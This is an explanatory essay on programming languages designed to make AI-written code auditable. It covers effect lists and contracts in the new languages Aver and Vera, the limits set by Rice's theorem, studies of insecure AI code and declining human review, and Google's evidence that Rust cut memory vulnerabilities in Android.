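# Auditable programming languages for AI-written code, and whether opaque programs can be restricted

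## What it means to audit a program, and what AI-written code changes

An auditable programming language is one designed to make it easier for someone other than a program's author to establish what the program does. Engineers have built such languages for decades, mostly for aircraft and weapons. Interest has widened because AI systems now write so much software. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (Bodkin, Sokhansanj and Hadfield, 2026) collects reports from Anthropic, OpenAI and Google that AI writes 75% or more of their new code. People cannot read all of that closely. One response is to have the AI write in a language that rules out whole classes of error and leaves the rest open to inspection. A more drastic response is to restrict programs that nobody can inspect. Both depend on what an audit can find out, and from what evidence.

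### One function in two forms

Source code is the text of a program in a programming language. The ten lines of source code below take money out of an account. They are written in C, an old language still used in a great deal of basic software.

```c
/* Takes amount out of balance; returns the new balance. */
int withdraw(int balance, int amount)
{
    if (amount > balance) {
        return balance;
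    }
    balance = balance - amount;
    record(amount);
    return balance;
}
```

If the customer asks for more than the account holds, the function returns the balance unchanged. Otherwise it subtracts the amount, calls a function named `record`, which presumably writes to a log, and returns what is left. An `int` is a whole number, positive or negative, that takes up 32 bits on most machines.

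A processor cannot run this text directly, so a program called a compiler first translates it into a binary, which consists of machine instructions that the processor can run. On an ordinary Intel or AMD chip, the subtraction may become the two bytes 29 F3, which make the processor subtract the number in one storage slot from the number in another. The translation removes the comment and normally also removes the names `balance` and `amount`.

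Someone who reads the source learns that the numbers are money, and can therefore see a mistake. If the function is called with a balance of 100 and an amount of −50, the subtraction goes ahead because −50 is not greater than 100, and the withdrawal raises the customer's balance to 150. Someone who has only the binary finds a comparison, a subtraction and a jump to another address, and nothing there looks wrong, because subtracting a negative number is valid arithmetic. The advantage of auditing the binary is that it is the code that will actually run. A faulty or tampered compiler can turn harmless source into a harmful binary, so anyone who audits the source is relying on the compiler. The compiler is therefore part of the trusted base, which is everything that must be correct for a check to be reliable.

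### Four kinds of check

The reader found the negative withdrawal only because they knew what a withdrawal is and thought to check for a negative amount. They also have only the name of `record` to go on unless they open that function too.

A test runs the function on chosen inputs and compares the result with the right answer. A test with a balance of 100 and an amount of 30 returns 70, and one with a balance of 100 and an amount of 200 returns 100. Both results are correct, so these tests miss the bug. Testing every input would take about 585 years at a billion pairs a second, because two 32-bit numbers make about 1.8 × 10¹⁹ pairs.

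Type checking happens before the program runs. A type system is a set of rules about what kind of value each part of a program may hold or return. C's rules allow the function, since −50 is a valid `int`. In a stricter language, the programmer could declare a type for amounts of zero or more. Code that passed in a number of unknown sign would then fail to compile until its author specified what happens when the number is negative. Some type systems also track effects, which are whatever a function does besides returning a value, such as writing a file or using the network. `record` has an effect, but the heading of `withdraw` doesn't show it. In a language that tracks effects, the heading must include it, so a reviewer can see it without reading the body.

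Formal verification proves that a program meets its specification for every permitted input. The programmer first writes the specification, a precise statement of what the program must do, but not how. A contract is a specification for a single function. It defines what must be true before the function runs and what will be true afterward. Suppose the contract for `withdraw` requires that the new balance never exceed the old one. A prover, a program that tries to derive this property logically from the code, will fail. It may report an amount of −50 as a counterexample, because withdrawing a negative amount raises the balance. Once the programmer adds the condition that the amount is never negative, the prover succeeds.

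Its weakness is the specification. Suppose the contract required only that an account that starts at zero or above never ends below zero. If we ignore numbers too large for 32 bits, the faulty function meets this requirement even when a withdrawal is negative, so the prover would pass it.

### Rice's theorem

No tool can replace all this with a yes-or-no answer that is correct for every program. In 1953 the mathematician Henry Gordon Rice published a theorem about questions on what programs do, as opposed to what their text looks like. If the answer to such a question is yes for some programs and no for others, no procedure can answer it correctly for every program.

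Suppose a tool could determine whether any given program ever pays out fifty dollars. For any program P, one could write a new program that runs P in isolation and pays out fifty dollars after P finishes. The new program pays out if and only if P finishes, so the tool could also be used to determine whether P finishes or runs forever. Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no procedure can do this for every program.

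A checker for a general-purpose language must therefore reject some good programs, miss some bad ones, or sometimes give no answer. Strict type systems mostly err in the first way, rejecting some harmless programs that the programmer then has to rewrite. Tests and bug-finding tools miss some bad programs, and provers often run out of time before reaching an answer. It is still possible to prove a particular program correct, though the theorem is often misread as ruling this out. Designers can also limit every loop and the memory in a language so that every question about its programs can be answered in principle, but programs that need to exceed those limits can't be written in it.

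Using AI to check the code does not avoid this limit. Livshits (2026), in *LLMs + Security = Trouble*, points out that an automated attacker searches with a limited budget, while the flaws most valuable to a criminal appear only under rare chains of conditions. Its failure to find a flaw is therefore weak evidence that none exists, and a later model may search parts of the program that this one missed.

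### How flawed AI-written code is

AI models often write insecure code in security tests, though how often depends a good deal on who chose the tasks. The *2026 GenAI Code Security Report* (2026) from Veracode, which sells security testing, reports an average pass rate of 56% across more than 100 models, with no improvement over time. The best model in its latest round, GPT-5.5, reached 68%. *Broken by Default* (2026) gave 500 prompts to each of seven mostly older models and found that 55.8% of the outputs were vulnerable.

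The most demanding test, *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (Wu, Ge and colleagues, 2026), removed the code containing each of 150 real vulnerabilities and had six AI agents rewrite it from a description that didn't mention security. Hidden tests then checked whether the code worked and whether a replay of the attack succeeded. Depending on the agent, 73.6% to 91.3% of the rewrites worked, but the best agent, Claude Fable 5, produced code that was both working and secure in 25.1% of tasks. Adding one sentence asking for secure code raised that rate by 15 to 21 percentage points for three of the four models retested, though most tasks still failed. The 25.1% figure is not a rate for ordinary code, because every task came from a place where earlier code had been vulnerable, and the selection of public vulnerabilities favoured hard ones.

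Studies disagree about whether AI code is less secure than human code. Improta, Liguori and Cotroneo (2026), in *What is the Difference Between Me and You?*, paired 787,562 human functions with AI versions written from the same short descriptions and ran automatic analysers over both. The AI versions had more security findings, and more severe ones, in Python and Java, but fewer high-severity findings in C. Mao, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *A Large-Scale Comprehensive Measurement of AI-Generated Code in Real-World Repositories*, studied AI code that programmers had accepted into public projects and matched it with older human code from the same projects. The AI code raised fewer alerts, 10.04 against 13.56 per thousand lines, and about as many high-risk alerts. The two studies nearly contradict each other by language, since C is where AI code looks worse in Mao and colleagues' sample.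 The most likely reason is that the first study measured raw AI output, while the second measured code that programmers had selected and edited. Aitel and Geer (2025), in *AI and Secure Code Generation*, wrote that experts no longer knew whether AI code was safer, riskier or vulnerable in different ways, which still seems about right as a comparison with human code.

The evidence is clearer about the kinds of flaws in AI-written code than about their number. In the tests by Wu and colleagues, agents did best on memory safety, such as not reading past the end of an array, but only 34.3% of those attempts were both working and secure. They nearly always failed when the defence depended on an unstated policy. When the task was to withhold certain data, only 0.7% of attempts succeeded. Help Net Security's *The AI code vulnerabilities that grow with your app* (2026) reports that the security firm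 Theori had AI agents build 28 applications and confirmed 434 flaws in them. Textbook injection attacks, in which hostile input runs as a command, barely appeared. Missing limits on resources made up 21% of the findings. Failures to check who may see which records rose from 11% of findings in small applications to 28% in a large rewritten one. This matters for the case for strict languages, because a language can prevent reads past the end of an array, but somebody still has to write down which customers may see which invoices.

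Some of these flaws have reached published software. Georgia Tech researchers traced six newly disclosed vulnerabilities to AI-written code in January 2026, 15 in February and at least 35 in March, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Security Researchers Sound the Alarm on Vulnerabilities in AI-Generated Code*. The rise may be due to more AI code or better tracing as much as to worse code.

### Who reads it

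Programmers usually submit a change as a pull request, which a colleague reviews before it joins the shared code. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) followed 802 developers at one software company from January 2024 to April 2026. In June 2025 the company's chief technology officer told staff to use AI to double their output. By April 2026 the average active developer wrote 44.3 pull requests a month, 2.09 times the early 2025 baseline of 21.2. This raw figure covers the 564 developers with at least three active months. The paper's preferred estimate is that AI itself multiplied output by 1.46.

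The number of reviewers grew much more slowly than the number of changes, so each reviewer's load doubled. The share of pull requests reviewed by a person fell from 89% to 68%, and the share with a written human comment fell from about 39% to 21%, while AI review rose from about 19% to 84%. The proportion of changes that developers later reversed stayed flat, which is evidence against a sudden collapse in quality, although developers can't reverse a change because of a defect nobody has noticed yet.

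Open-source projects show a similar but uneven pattern. In the AI projects that Bodkin and colleagues studied, people still reviewed about 80% of the pull requests with no detectable AI use and somewhat fewer of the others, but reviewers' comments per thousand lines had roughly halved since early 2024. For accounts that submit changes in bulk, the review rate fell below 30%. *On Autopilot?* (2026), which used a different sample, reports that 79.0% of merged human-and-AI pull requests received no outside review or comment. People inside AI companies may be reading less code too. Bodkin and colleagues quote the OpenAI researcher Daniel Selsam: "I myself barely look at raw code anymore."

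It helps to distinguish code that someone has reviewed, code that is readable but unreviewed, and code with no readable form. Much of what AI writes now is readable but unreviewed. An investigator can still read it after an accident, and a scanner can check it at any time. Those options are mostly unavailable for code with no readable form, such as a binary that an AI system generates directly, without source code.

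### The safety argument and where it can break

The case for auditable languages depends on four claims. First, the language rules out some errors, so no program the compiler accepts contains them. Second, it exposes what it does not rule out by putting effects and contracts where a checker will look. Third, a person or tool checks what the language exposes. Fourth, the program that runs is the one that passed the check, though this assumption usually goes unstated. If any of these claims is false, the argument fails.

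The figures on review raise the most doubt about the third link. A visible contract protects nobody if the reviewer approves it without reading it, which Livshits expects to happen. He argues that unless verification is fully automatic, developers must keep validating specifications and settling ambiguous cases, and that people who habitually accept every change the AI proposes will do this badly. Andrew Wesie, Theori's chief technology officer, told Help Net Security that automated tools must take over line-by-line review, while people keep responsibility for threat models and overall design. On either view, people will read only a little, so a language that reduces what they must read is worth more, provided that what remains is the part that matters.

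### Rules, and three questions to ask of them

A restriction can apply to a program's form, its properties or its origin. A rule on form might require a program to come with source code, or ban deliberately scrambled text. A rule on properties requires the author to show something about the program, for instance that it never touches memory outside its own, whatever language it was written in. Rice's theorem implies that no inspector can detect every breach, so such a rule usually puts the burden of proof on the author and accepts that some good programs will fail. A rule on origin concerns how people made the program. Aitel and Geer call for records of the models, prompts and datasets behind a piece of code. Bodkin and colleagues want auditors to question the people responsible for AI research code, without AI help, and to halt releases when nobody can explain it.

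A program can satisfy one of these rules and break another. A binary can be proven to stay within its memory limits and still break a rule that requires source code. The `withdraw` function satisfies any rule on form but breaks a sensible rule on properties, and nothing in it shows whether a person or a model wrote it.

For any restriction, we can ask whether a breach is detectable from the program itself. Breaches of restrictions on a program's form often are. For restrictions on its origin, the evidence is mixed. Improta and colleagues could separate raw AI output from human code by its statistical regularity, but Mao and colleagues found AI code in real projects by searching for comments in which programmers admitted using AI, and measured only small structural differences from human code.

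Only some programs have to pass a gatekeeper, meaning a body or piece of software that can refuse a program before anyone runs or distributes it. Apps for a phone with a single app store go through one, but a program that someone compiles at home on their own ordinary computer does not.

The remaining questions are how much money and speed developers would lose by complying with the rule, which programs they could no longer write, and how those losses compare with what someone could gain by cheating.

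One objection to restricting opaque programs is that a ban would drive their use underground. In its strongest form, the argument starts from the fact that software costs almost nothing to copy and needs no special site to run on, so inspectors have nowhere to visit. If opaque programs turn out to be faster or cheaper than readable ones, a ban would increase the reward for using them, because law-abiding rivals would have given up that advantage. Firms that suspected their competitors of cheating would then have a reason to cheat too. They could hide it by having an AI system write plausible source code to file beside a binary that was not compiled from it, and few people would check that the two match. The firms that obeyed would be the careful ones, whose programs were already the least dangerous. The rest would stop publishing, reporting accidents and asking outside researchers for help,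 and nobody would build the inspection tools that a lawful industry would have paid for. As a result, nearly as much opaque code would be in use, and people would know far less about where it was running.

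## Aver and Vera: languages designed for AI to write and people to check

The temptation to cheat on a ban on opaque programs would depend partly on how hard it is to write readable ones. Two languages that appeared in early 2026 try to make this easier, on the theory that tedious typing isn't a burden for an AI. In Aver, created by the programmer Szymon Teżewski, every function must list how it may interact with anything outside the program. In Vera, created by Alasdair Allan, every function must have a contract, and variables have no names.

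### A refund in Aver

The function below sends a payment company a request to refund an order. It is modeled on a function in Aver's documentation that fetches an exchange rate.

```
fn refund(orderId: String, card: String) -> Result<HttpResponse, String>
    ? "Sends a refund request to the payment company."
    ! [Http.get]
    Http.get("https://pay.example.com/refund/{orderId}/{card}")
```

The first line gives the function's inputs, two pieces of text, and its output, which is either a reply from the web or an error message. The line with the question mark describes the function in English. The line with the exclamation mark lists its effects, and the only one here is `Http.get`, which fetches a web address. The last line does the work. (A real payment company would want a different kind of web request, but the list of effects would work the same way.)

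Suppose the AI later adds a line that saves the card number to a file, perhaps for debugging. File operations belong to a group of effects called `Disk`, which isn't on the list, so Aver rejects the program before it runs. Aver also rejects a program if the AI leaves out a declaration the code needs. In *A prompt is a request. A language is the law*, Teżewski gives the example of an AI that writes a function to fetch data from the web and forgets to declare the web request.

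The AI can fix the error by removing the file write or by adding the write to the list, and Aver will accept either. If the AI adds it to the list, every function that calls `refund` must list it too, and so must the functions that call those, up to the top of the program. The AI can still write the file, but only by changing the headings, so someone who reads only the headings will see the change. A simple script could also hold back any change that adds an effect until a person approves it, which may matter more because people now read so few changes.

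### A leak through the permitted call

Now suppose the AI leaves the effects alone and changes `pay.example.com` to `pay.example.net`, an address that belongs to someone else. The function now sends the customer's card number to a stranger, but its heading hasn't changed. Aver accepts it because the function has permission to fetch a web address.

Aver has a partial answer, a separate settings file that limits where each effect can reach. For the refund, it would contain these two lines:

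```
[effects.Http]
hosts = ["pay.example.com"]
```

The altered function would still pass the type check, but Aver would block the request when the program ran. This works only if the AI can't edit the settings file, or if someone notices when it does. Before putting an Aver program into service, developers normally use Aver's compiler to translate it into Rust, an older general-purpose language. The Rust version can also apply the limits, but only if the developers choose the right option when they compile it.

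A program restricted to a correct list of addresses can still leak data. Many programs need to reach a service that other people can read, such as a public code host or a shared log, and a program can put a card number in a message to it. To prevent this in the language itself, the type system would have to track where each piece of data is allowed to go, so that a card number couldn't become part of a web address without permission. Researchers have built such type systems, but they are laborious to use. Aver's effects cover only the kind of access, and so do Vera's. In Vera, the heading of this function would list `Http` but no destination.

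### What Aver checks and what it only records

Aver leaves out many ordinary features because they let a program do things that aren't visible in the code a reader is looking at. It has no loops, so a function that repeats a step must call itself or use a built-in list operation. It has no closures, which are functions that carry values from the place where they were defined, so a function can't depend on a value captured elsewhere. Variables never change after they receive a value. Functions report failure by returning an error that the caller has to handle, instead of interrupting the program. Teżewski says he deliberately made the language inconvenient to write by hand, since the AI will do the writing.

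Besides the English description, an Aver program can contain `decision` blocks that record what the author chose, what they rejected and why. One block in the documentation explains that the program returns errors because "Invisible exceptions lose money at runtime." These notes help reviewers, or another AI that has to change the code later. Aver can check that the functions named in a decision exist, but it can't check that the reasons are true or that the description matches the code.

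Aver's own documentation shows the problem. It describes a function called `processPayment` as one that "Validates and records the charge" without using the network or disk. The function has no effects, so the second half of that description is right, and the compiler enforces it. But the function doesn't record anything, and couldn't without effects. It returns an error if the amount is zero and a made-up transaction number otherwise.

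Aver also requires tests in the program itself. If a function has no effects and does anything non-trivial, `aver check` reports an error unless a `verify` block gives examples of what it should return. A reader can then compare the code with the expected behaviour beside it, though the expected behaviour may itself be wrong. The documentation's `charge` function rejects a charge of zero and accepts every other number, and one of its examples gives success as the correct result for a charge of −1. This is close to the bug in `withdraw`, except that here the bug is also written into the test. An automated check would pass that example, but a reader who knows what a charge is could spot the mistake quickly, which is a point in favour of the format.

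Examples work badly for functions with effects, such as web requests, because the replies may differ each time. For these functions, the developer runs the program once against the real services while Aver records each effect and its reply. Aver can then rerun the program using the saved replies instead of the network, and report any difference in the program's behavior. This is a good way to check whether an AI's rewrite that was meant to be harmless changed anything. It covers only the recorded situations, so if the payment company never refused a refund during the recording, the replay won't show how the program handles a refusal.

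For stronger guarantees, Aver can translate functions without effects into Lean, a language in which a small program called a kernel checks mathematical proofs. The author writes a law, such as that `add(a, b)` always equals `add(b, a)`, with a few sample values. `aver verify` tests the law only on those samples. When Aver exports the law to Lean, it attempts a proof for all values, but only for certain forms of law. Other laws remain checks on the samples, and the documentation states this difference clearly. For functions with effects, the exported proof treats responses from outside the program as unknown inputs.

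The newest versions of Aver can attach a certificate to a compiled program. The certificate applies to the exact bytes of that program, and a separate tool uses Lean to check it. This is meant to guarantee that the program that runs is the one that passed the check. This matters especially for Aver because its creator had Claude and Codex, two AI coding tools, write much of Aver itself in Rust, and has said he can't verify all of their code. The documentation now lists certificates as the language's first aim, ahead of readability ("Readability comes second").

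### A division in Vera

Vera relies on contracts more than on reading. This function divides a restaurant bill among the guests.

```
public fn split_bill(@Int, @Int -> @Int)
  requires(@Int.0 != 0)
  ensures(@Int.result == @Int.1 / @Int.0)
  effects(pure)
{
  @Int.1 / @Int.0
}
```

The function takes two whole numbers and returns another. Since variables have no names, the code refers to each one by its type and its position, counting back from the most recent. `@Int.0` is the second input, the number of guests, and `@Int.1` is the first, the total. The `requires` line is the precondition that the number of guests isn't zero. The `ensures` line is the postcondition, which specifies the result. `effects(pure)` means the function has no effects.

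Vera checks the postcondition with Z3, an automatic solver from Microsoft. Z3 assumes that the precondition is true, works out the result from the body, and searches for two numbers that would make the postcondition false. If it can show that none exist, Vera has proved the postcondition for every input. The proof is trivial here because the postcondition repeats the body.

The precondition is more useful, because Vera checks it wherever another function calls `split_bill`. Suppose the AI writes this caller:

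```
public fn bill_per_guest(@Int, @Int -> @Int)
  requires(true)
  ensures(true)
  effects(pure)
{
  split_bill(@Int.1, @Int.0)
}
```

`requires(true)` means that the caller accepts any numbers. Z3 therefore finds that zero guests would break the contract of `split_bill`, and Vera reports an error. If the AI changes the caller's precondition to `requires(@Int.0 > 0)`, the check succeeds, and whatever calls `bill_per_guest` must rule out zero. Eventually, some function that takes outside input, such as one that reads a web form, has to test for zero and decide how to handle it, which C would not force the programmer to consider.

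The first of two limits is that Z3 can't decide every contract. When it can't, Vera tests the contract while the program runs, so a mistake stops the program instead of preventing it from compiling. This isn't rare. Vera's leading example of effects is a function that searches the web and has an AI summarise the results, and its precondition is that the search text isn't empty. According to Vera's guide for AI models, Z3 usually can't reason about the length of a text that isn't fixed in advance, because Vera counts bytes and Z3 has no matching operation.

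The second limit is that a contract can be empty. Every function must have one, but `requires(true)` and `ensures(true)` satisfy the rule without guaranteeing anything. The web search function has `ensures(true)` as its postcondition, as do many of the examples in the guide. An AI can use empty contracts to get its code to compile, so anyone who wants to rely on Vera's contracts has to look for the ones that say `true`.

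### Whether names help

Vera drops names because, according to its documentation, AI models often choose misleading names, reuse them wrongly or lose track of which name goes with which value. That is plausible, but numbering has its own problems, and the best example is in the same documentation. The documentation opens with a function called `safe_divide`, which is the same as `split_bill` except that the two numbers are swapped. Its body divides `@Int.0` by `@Int.1`, so it divides the second input by the first. Someone who calls `safe_divide(10, 2)` expecting 5 will get 2 divided by 10, which rounds down to 0. The contract doesn't catch the mistake, because the postcondition has the numbers in the same order as the body, and the precondition only requires the first input, 10, not to be zero. In Aver, `safeDivide(10, 2)` returns 5.

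An AI can make this mistake as easily as a person. Vera's guide for models calls slot order (the numbering of variables) "the most common source of bugs in Vera programs". It advises against relying on intuition and recommends a command that prints which number refers to which input. The error is hard to notice in testing because many operations, such as addition, give the same answer in either order.

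The numbers also change meaning within a function. The guide has an example much like this one:

```
  let @Int = @Int.0 * 2;
  let @Int = @Int.0 + 1;
  @Int.0
```

If the function receives 5, the first line computes 10, the second computes 11 and the third returns 11. `@Int.0` means 5 on the first line, 10 on the second and 11 on the third. If someone later inserts another whole number above the last line, `@Int.0` on the last line will refer to the new number, even though that line's text hasn't changed. This is especially bad for code review, because programmers usually read the changed lines and skim the rest.

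Using numbers instead of variable names makes no difference to Z3, because the meaning of a name plays no part in solving. Numbers do remove a step from the compiler, which would otherwise have to determine which of two variables with the same name a reference refers to.

The evidence on models is mixed. The case for Vera is strongest where the alternative is a misleading name. *Do Machines Struggle Where Humans Do?* (Le, Nguyen and Nguyen, 2026) tested whether small models could predict what short functions return. A 7-billion-parameter reasoning model based on DeepSeek-R1 was right 63.8% of the time with the original names, 64.2% with meaningless names and 51.8% with misleading ones. Stronger models can also be misled. *Poisoned Identifiers Survive LLM Deobfuscation* (2026) found that Claude Opus 4.6 kept wrong but plausible names when it rebuilt readable code from scrambled code.

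Good names do help models, though. In *When Names Disappear*, Le, Pham and colleagues (2025) replaced the names in realistic programs and had models summarise the code. GPT-4o's score for describing the purpose of a whole class (a group of related functions and data) fell from 87.3 to 58.7 out of 100, and DeepSeek V3's fell from 87.7 to 76.7. GPT-4o recognised one program as a Minesweeper game with the names in place, but without them it could only describe the updates to a grid line by line. Accuracy in predicting the output of the same kind of program also fell, from 85.7% to 76.1%, even though names don't affect the output. Summaries of competition puzzles barely changed, probably because the names in those are mostly single letters already.

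*Clean Code is Good For AIs, Too* describes an informal two-day test in which Claude tried different coding styles and preferred long, descriptive names, saying that without them it took more time and tokens to work out what a variable was for. It's unclear how much weight to give a model's explanation of its own preferences, but the result counts against Vera's approach to variable names.

The only figures here for people come from an earlier experiment that Le, Nguyen and Nguyen used for comparison. Fifty computer science students predicted the output of functions of fewer than 15 lines. When meaningless names replaced the original ones, the students' accuracy fell only slightly, from 40.5% to 38.7%, but beginners' accuracy fell from 34.2% to 26.7%. The experiment probably understates how much names help an auditor, because the students only had to trace the steps, whereas the auditor of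 `withdraw` had to know that the numbers were money. Each meaningless name also referred to the same variable throughout, unlike Vera's numbers.

Having no name seems worse than having a good one but better than having a bad one. Vera's choice makes sense if models often choose bad names, but none of these studies measured how often they do. Vera programs can still contain bad names because functions have names. For example, `safe_divide` is a misleading name for a function that most people would call with its inputs the wrong way round. A tool could show people a version with names and leave the numbers for the AI, but somebody would have to write the names and make sure they were right.

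### How well models write these languages

The obvious objection to a new language like Aver or Vera is that AI models have learned from almost no code written in it. Models already do noticeably better in Python than in some other established languages. In an unfamiliar language, they might make enough mistakes to cancel out the benefit of strict checking, or fall back on habits from languages they know.

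Both projects reply that a small language doesn't take much learning. An AI can read the full rules in its prompt and learn the rest from the compiler's error messages. If a function has no contract, Vera's error message explains what is missing, why Vera requires it and where the rule appears in the specification, and gives a sample contract to copy. Aver publishes a short file for models that lists the rules they most often get wrong.

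VeraBench, a set of tests that Allan also created, is the only published measurement of this for Vera. Its 50 problems range from simple arithmetic to programs with several functions and effects. Six models attempted them in Vera, Python and TypeScript, a version of JavaScript with type checking. Each Vera prompt included the language guide. The table shows how often the finished program produced the right output.

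| Model | Python | TypeScript | Vera |
|---|---|---|---|
| Kimi K2.5 | 86% | 91% | 100% |
| GPT-4.1 | 96% | 96% | 91% |
| Claude Opus 4 | 96% | 96% | 88% |
| Kimi K2 Turbo | 88% | 79% | 83% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 96% | 88% | 79% |
| GPT-4o | 93% | 83% | 78% |

Models did impressively well in a language they knew only from a document in the prompt. The project's summary goes further and says that the strongest models are about as good in Vera as in Python, at 93% each, but these figures are averages over only the first three models in the table. Over all six, the averages are 86.5% for Vera, 92.5% for Python and 88.8% for TypeScript. The summary also says that three models did better in Vera than in TypeScript, but the table shows only two. The third, Claude Sonnet 4, did better in Vera in an earlier round, and its result reversed when Allan ran the test again.

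That reversal shows how noisy the scores are. Each model had one attempt at each problem. Several scores, such as 91%, aren't possible out of 50, so this measure must cover fewer than 50 problems. I would not read much into Kimi K2.5's perfect score, and Allan himself calls the results early and says they need repeated trials.

In a second version of the test, which is more relevant to auditing, the models had to write the contracts themselves from an English description instead of being given them. Kimi K2.5 still scored 100%, but GPT-4.1 fell from 91% to 50%. If this pattern holds, models working in an unfamiliar language can write code to fit a contract more reliably than they can write the contract itself, which is the part people are supposed to rely on.

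All six models in the table are old by now. Newer models are probably better at this, because they are better at programming and some may have seen Vera code in training. VeraBench cites results from an older test, DafnyBench, in which models take programs in Dafny, a language with contracts much like Vera's, and add the hints that a prover needs. The success rate rose from 68% to 96% in under two years. But Dafny has existed since 2009, so those models had seen some Dafny code in training.

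There is less evidence for Aver. VeraBench can run its problems in Aver, but its published results include no Aver scores. Aver's documentation mentions a test that compares how easy Aver and several styles of Python are to review, using 108 code changes, but AI models did the reviewing. There seems to be no experiment on whether people catch more of the mistakes in Aver or Vera code than in code written in an ordinary language, although helping people check code is the main purpose of both languages.

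### New languages or existing ones

The other objection is that nobody needs a new language for this. Vera's documentation lists SPARK and Koka among the languages it borrows from. SPARK, a version of Ada for critical systems such as aircraft software, already has contracts that a prover can check. Koka includes effects in a function's type, as Aver does. Rust prevents many memory errors and has far more users than any of these. A company could have its AI write in SPARK, Koka or Rust, or in Python with a strict type checker, and run the result in a container that blocks access to files and the network.

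There are good reasons for this view. Existing languages have libraries, so the AI doesn't have to write its own code for things like encryption, where home-made code is often dangerous. People already know how to read these languages. Users have also found many of the bugs in their compilers over the years, while Vera was still at version 0.0.127 in the copy of its documentation with the `safe_divide` example.

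The argument for new languages is that older ones have ways around their own rules. Rust's `unsafe` keyword switches off some of its checks, and Python lets almost any function do almost anything. Someone who audits code in these languages has to make sure that the AI hasn't used these loopholes. A container applies to the whole program, so it can't replace a list of effects for each function. If one function needs the network, the container has to allow it for every function. Aver can limit network access to the functions that need it, and it checks this before the program runs.

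Still, a team can remove many of the exceptions in an existing language with a compiler setting or an extra checking tool. For example, it can forbid `unsafe` in its own Rust code or refuse any SPARK function without a contract. It is harder to add effect declarations for each function to a language whose libraries don't have them, and this seems to me the best reason to build a new language. The case for replacing variable names is weaker, because doing so makes programs harder for people to read and nobody has yet shown that it helps models write better programs.

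Other languages in this field include Universalis, AILANG, Onus and Jacquard. Universalis, by the language designer Erik Meijer, mixes ordinary sentences with small formulas so that people comfortable with spreadsheets can follow the program. AILANG, like Aver and Vera, lists effects in a function's heading, with separate ones for files, the network, the clock and calls to an AI model. Teżewski doesn't claim that Aver should replace general-purpose languages, and he grants that some of its programs look like those of any small, strict functional language. His translation into Rust lets a team write just the rules for refunds in Aver, where they are easiest to check, and everything else in a language it already knows.

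## Rust in Android and the AI port of Bun: what a strict language prevents

Rust, the language that Aver's compiler produces, has been widely used for years, so the evidence about it is much better than for Aver or Vera. Google has measured the effects of Android's move from C and C++ to Rust. In May 2026, one engineer used AI agents to translate Bun, a large and popular program, into Rust. People choose Rust mainly because it prevents most memory errors and is about as fast as C. Several governments recommend languages of this kind for the same reason.

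### A use-after-free

This C code stores a card number, gives the memory back and then prints it:

```c
char *card = malloc(20);
strcpy(card, "4111 1111 1111 1111");
free(card);
printf("%s\n", card);
```

`malloc` reserves 20 bytes of memory, and `free` releases them so the program can reuse them. The last line prints whatever is in those bytes now, which on a busy server could be another customer's data. If the program writes to released memory, an attacker who can influence what is stored there may be able to take control of the program. Programmers call any use of released memory a use-after-free. Other memory errors include reading or writing past the end of an array and freeing the same memory twice. C compilers sometimes warn about an example this short, but they can't track every pointer through a large program.

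Here is the same mistake in Rust:

```rust
let card = String::from("4111 1111 1111 1111");
drop(card);
println!("{card}");
```

This doesn't compile. In Rust, every value has exactly one owner, which here is the variable `card`. Passing the value to a function normally transfers ownership, and the old variable becomes unusable. `drop` takes ownership and frees the memory, so the compiler rejects the last line. Without `drop`, Rust frees the memory automatically at the end of the block of code that contains `card`.

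Most functions only need to look at a value, so Rust also lets them borrow it. The `&` below borrows the first item in a list:

```rust
let mut cards = vec![String::from("4111")];
let first = &cards[0];
cards.push(String::from("5500"));
println!("{first}");
```

Rust rejects this too. Adding an item to a full list can move the whole list to a larger block of memory, leaving `first` pointing to the old block. Rust lets a value have any number of readers or a single writer at one time, but not both. The compiler also checks that no borrow outlasts the value it refers to.

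Some necessary jobs, such as calling a C library or controlling hardware, are impossible under these rules, so Rust has the `unsafe` keyword. An `unsafe` block permits a few extra operations, mainly calling functions that the compiler can't check and following raw pointers, which are addresses it doesn't track. The other checks still apply. The programmer takes responsibility for the block, and an auditor can find every such block by searching for the word. Google's *Memory Safe Languages in Android 13* (2022) describes Android's code for ultra-wideband, a short-range radio, which used `unsafe` twice. By paying extra attention to those two places, the team found a possible timing bug and guarded against it.

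### Google's Android figures

Memory errors made up 76% of Android's vulnerabilities in 2019 and 24% in 2024. In 2025 they fell below 20% for the first time, according to *Rust in Android* (Vander Stoep, 2025). Their number also fell, from 223 in 2019 to fewer than 50 in 2024 (The Hacker News, 2025), so the lower share isn't just due to a rise in other flaws. These figures cover all of Android's code, including Java and Kotlin, which also prevent most memory errors, so the decline isn't due to Rust alone.

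Android has about 5 million lines of Rust, in which Google has found one potential memory vulnerability, or 0.2 per million lines. Google's historical figure for C and C++ is about 1,000 per million. The vulnerability was in CrabbyAVIF, an image library whose `unsafe` code could write past the end of a block of memory. Google fixed it before any public release. Android's memory allocator would have stopped an attack anyway, because it puts inaccessible memory around large blocks.

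A rate based on one case is imprecise, but even if five more such flaws were found, Rust's rate would still be about 800 times lower than the rate for C and C++.

Most of Android's Rust is recent, while researchers and attackers have had many years to find flaws in its C and C++, so more flaws will probably emerge in the Rust. But new code usually has more flaws than old code. A comment in *5 million Rust LOC*, an online discussion of Google's figures, cites an earlier Google finding that five-year-old Android code had 7.4 times fewer vulnerabilities per line than new code. Neither effect seems large enough to explain a difference of a thousand times or more.

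Google also found that developers rolled back medium and large Rust changes about a quarter as often as C++ changes of similar size. Rust changes needed about 20% fewer revisions and spent about 25% less time in review. Quicker review could mean less careful review, but then one would expect more rollbacks. The lower rollback rate is also the best sign here that Rust helps with more than memory safety, since developers roll back changes for many reasons.

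Vander Stoep compared changes of similar size and included only Google's own Android developers, many of whom write both Rust and C++. This weakens but doesn't remove the objection that better programmers choose Rust, because nobody assigned the work at random. Teams may also use Rust for new, self-contained components and C++ for changes to old code that much else depends on, and such changes are riskier in any language. Developers also got better at Rust over time, which Vander Stoep suspects explains much of the improvement in review times between 2023 and 2024.

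### Well-typed code from a model

None of this shows that Rust helps when an AI writes the code, but the tests by Wu and colleagues showed that AI models make the errors that Rust prevents.

A type system can constrain a model's code as the model writes it. A language model produces text in small pieces called tokens, and at each step it assigns a probability to every possible next token. Mündler and colleagues (2025), in *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*, built a checker for a large part of TypeScript that removes any token that would make a well-typed program impossible to complete. The model then chooses from the remaining tokens.

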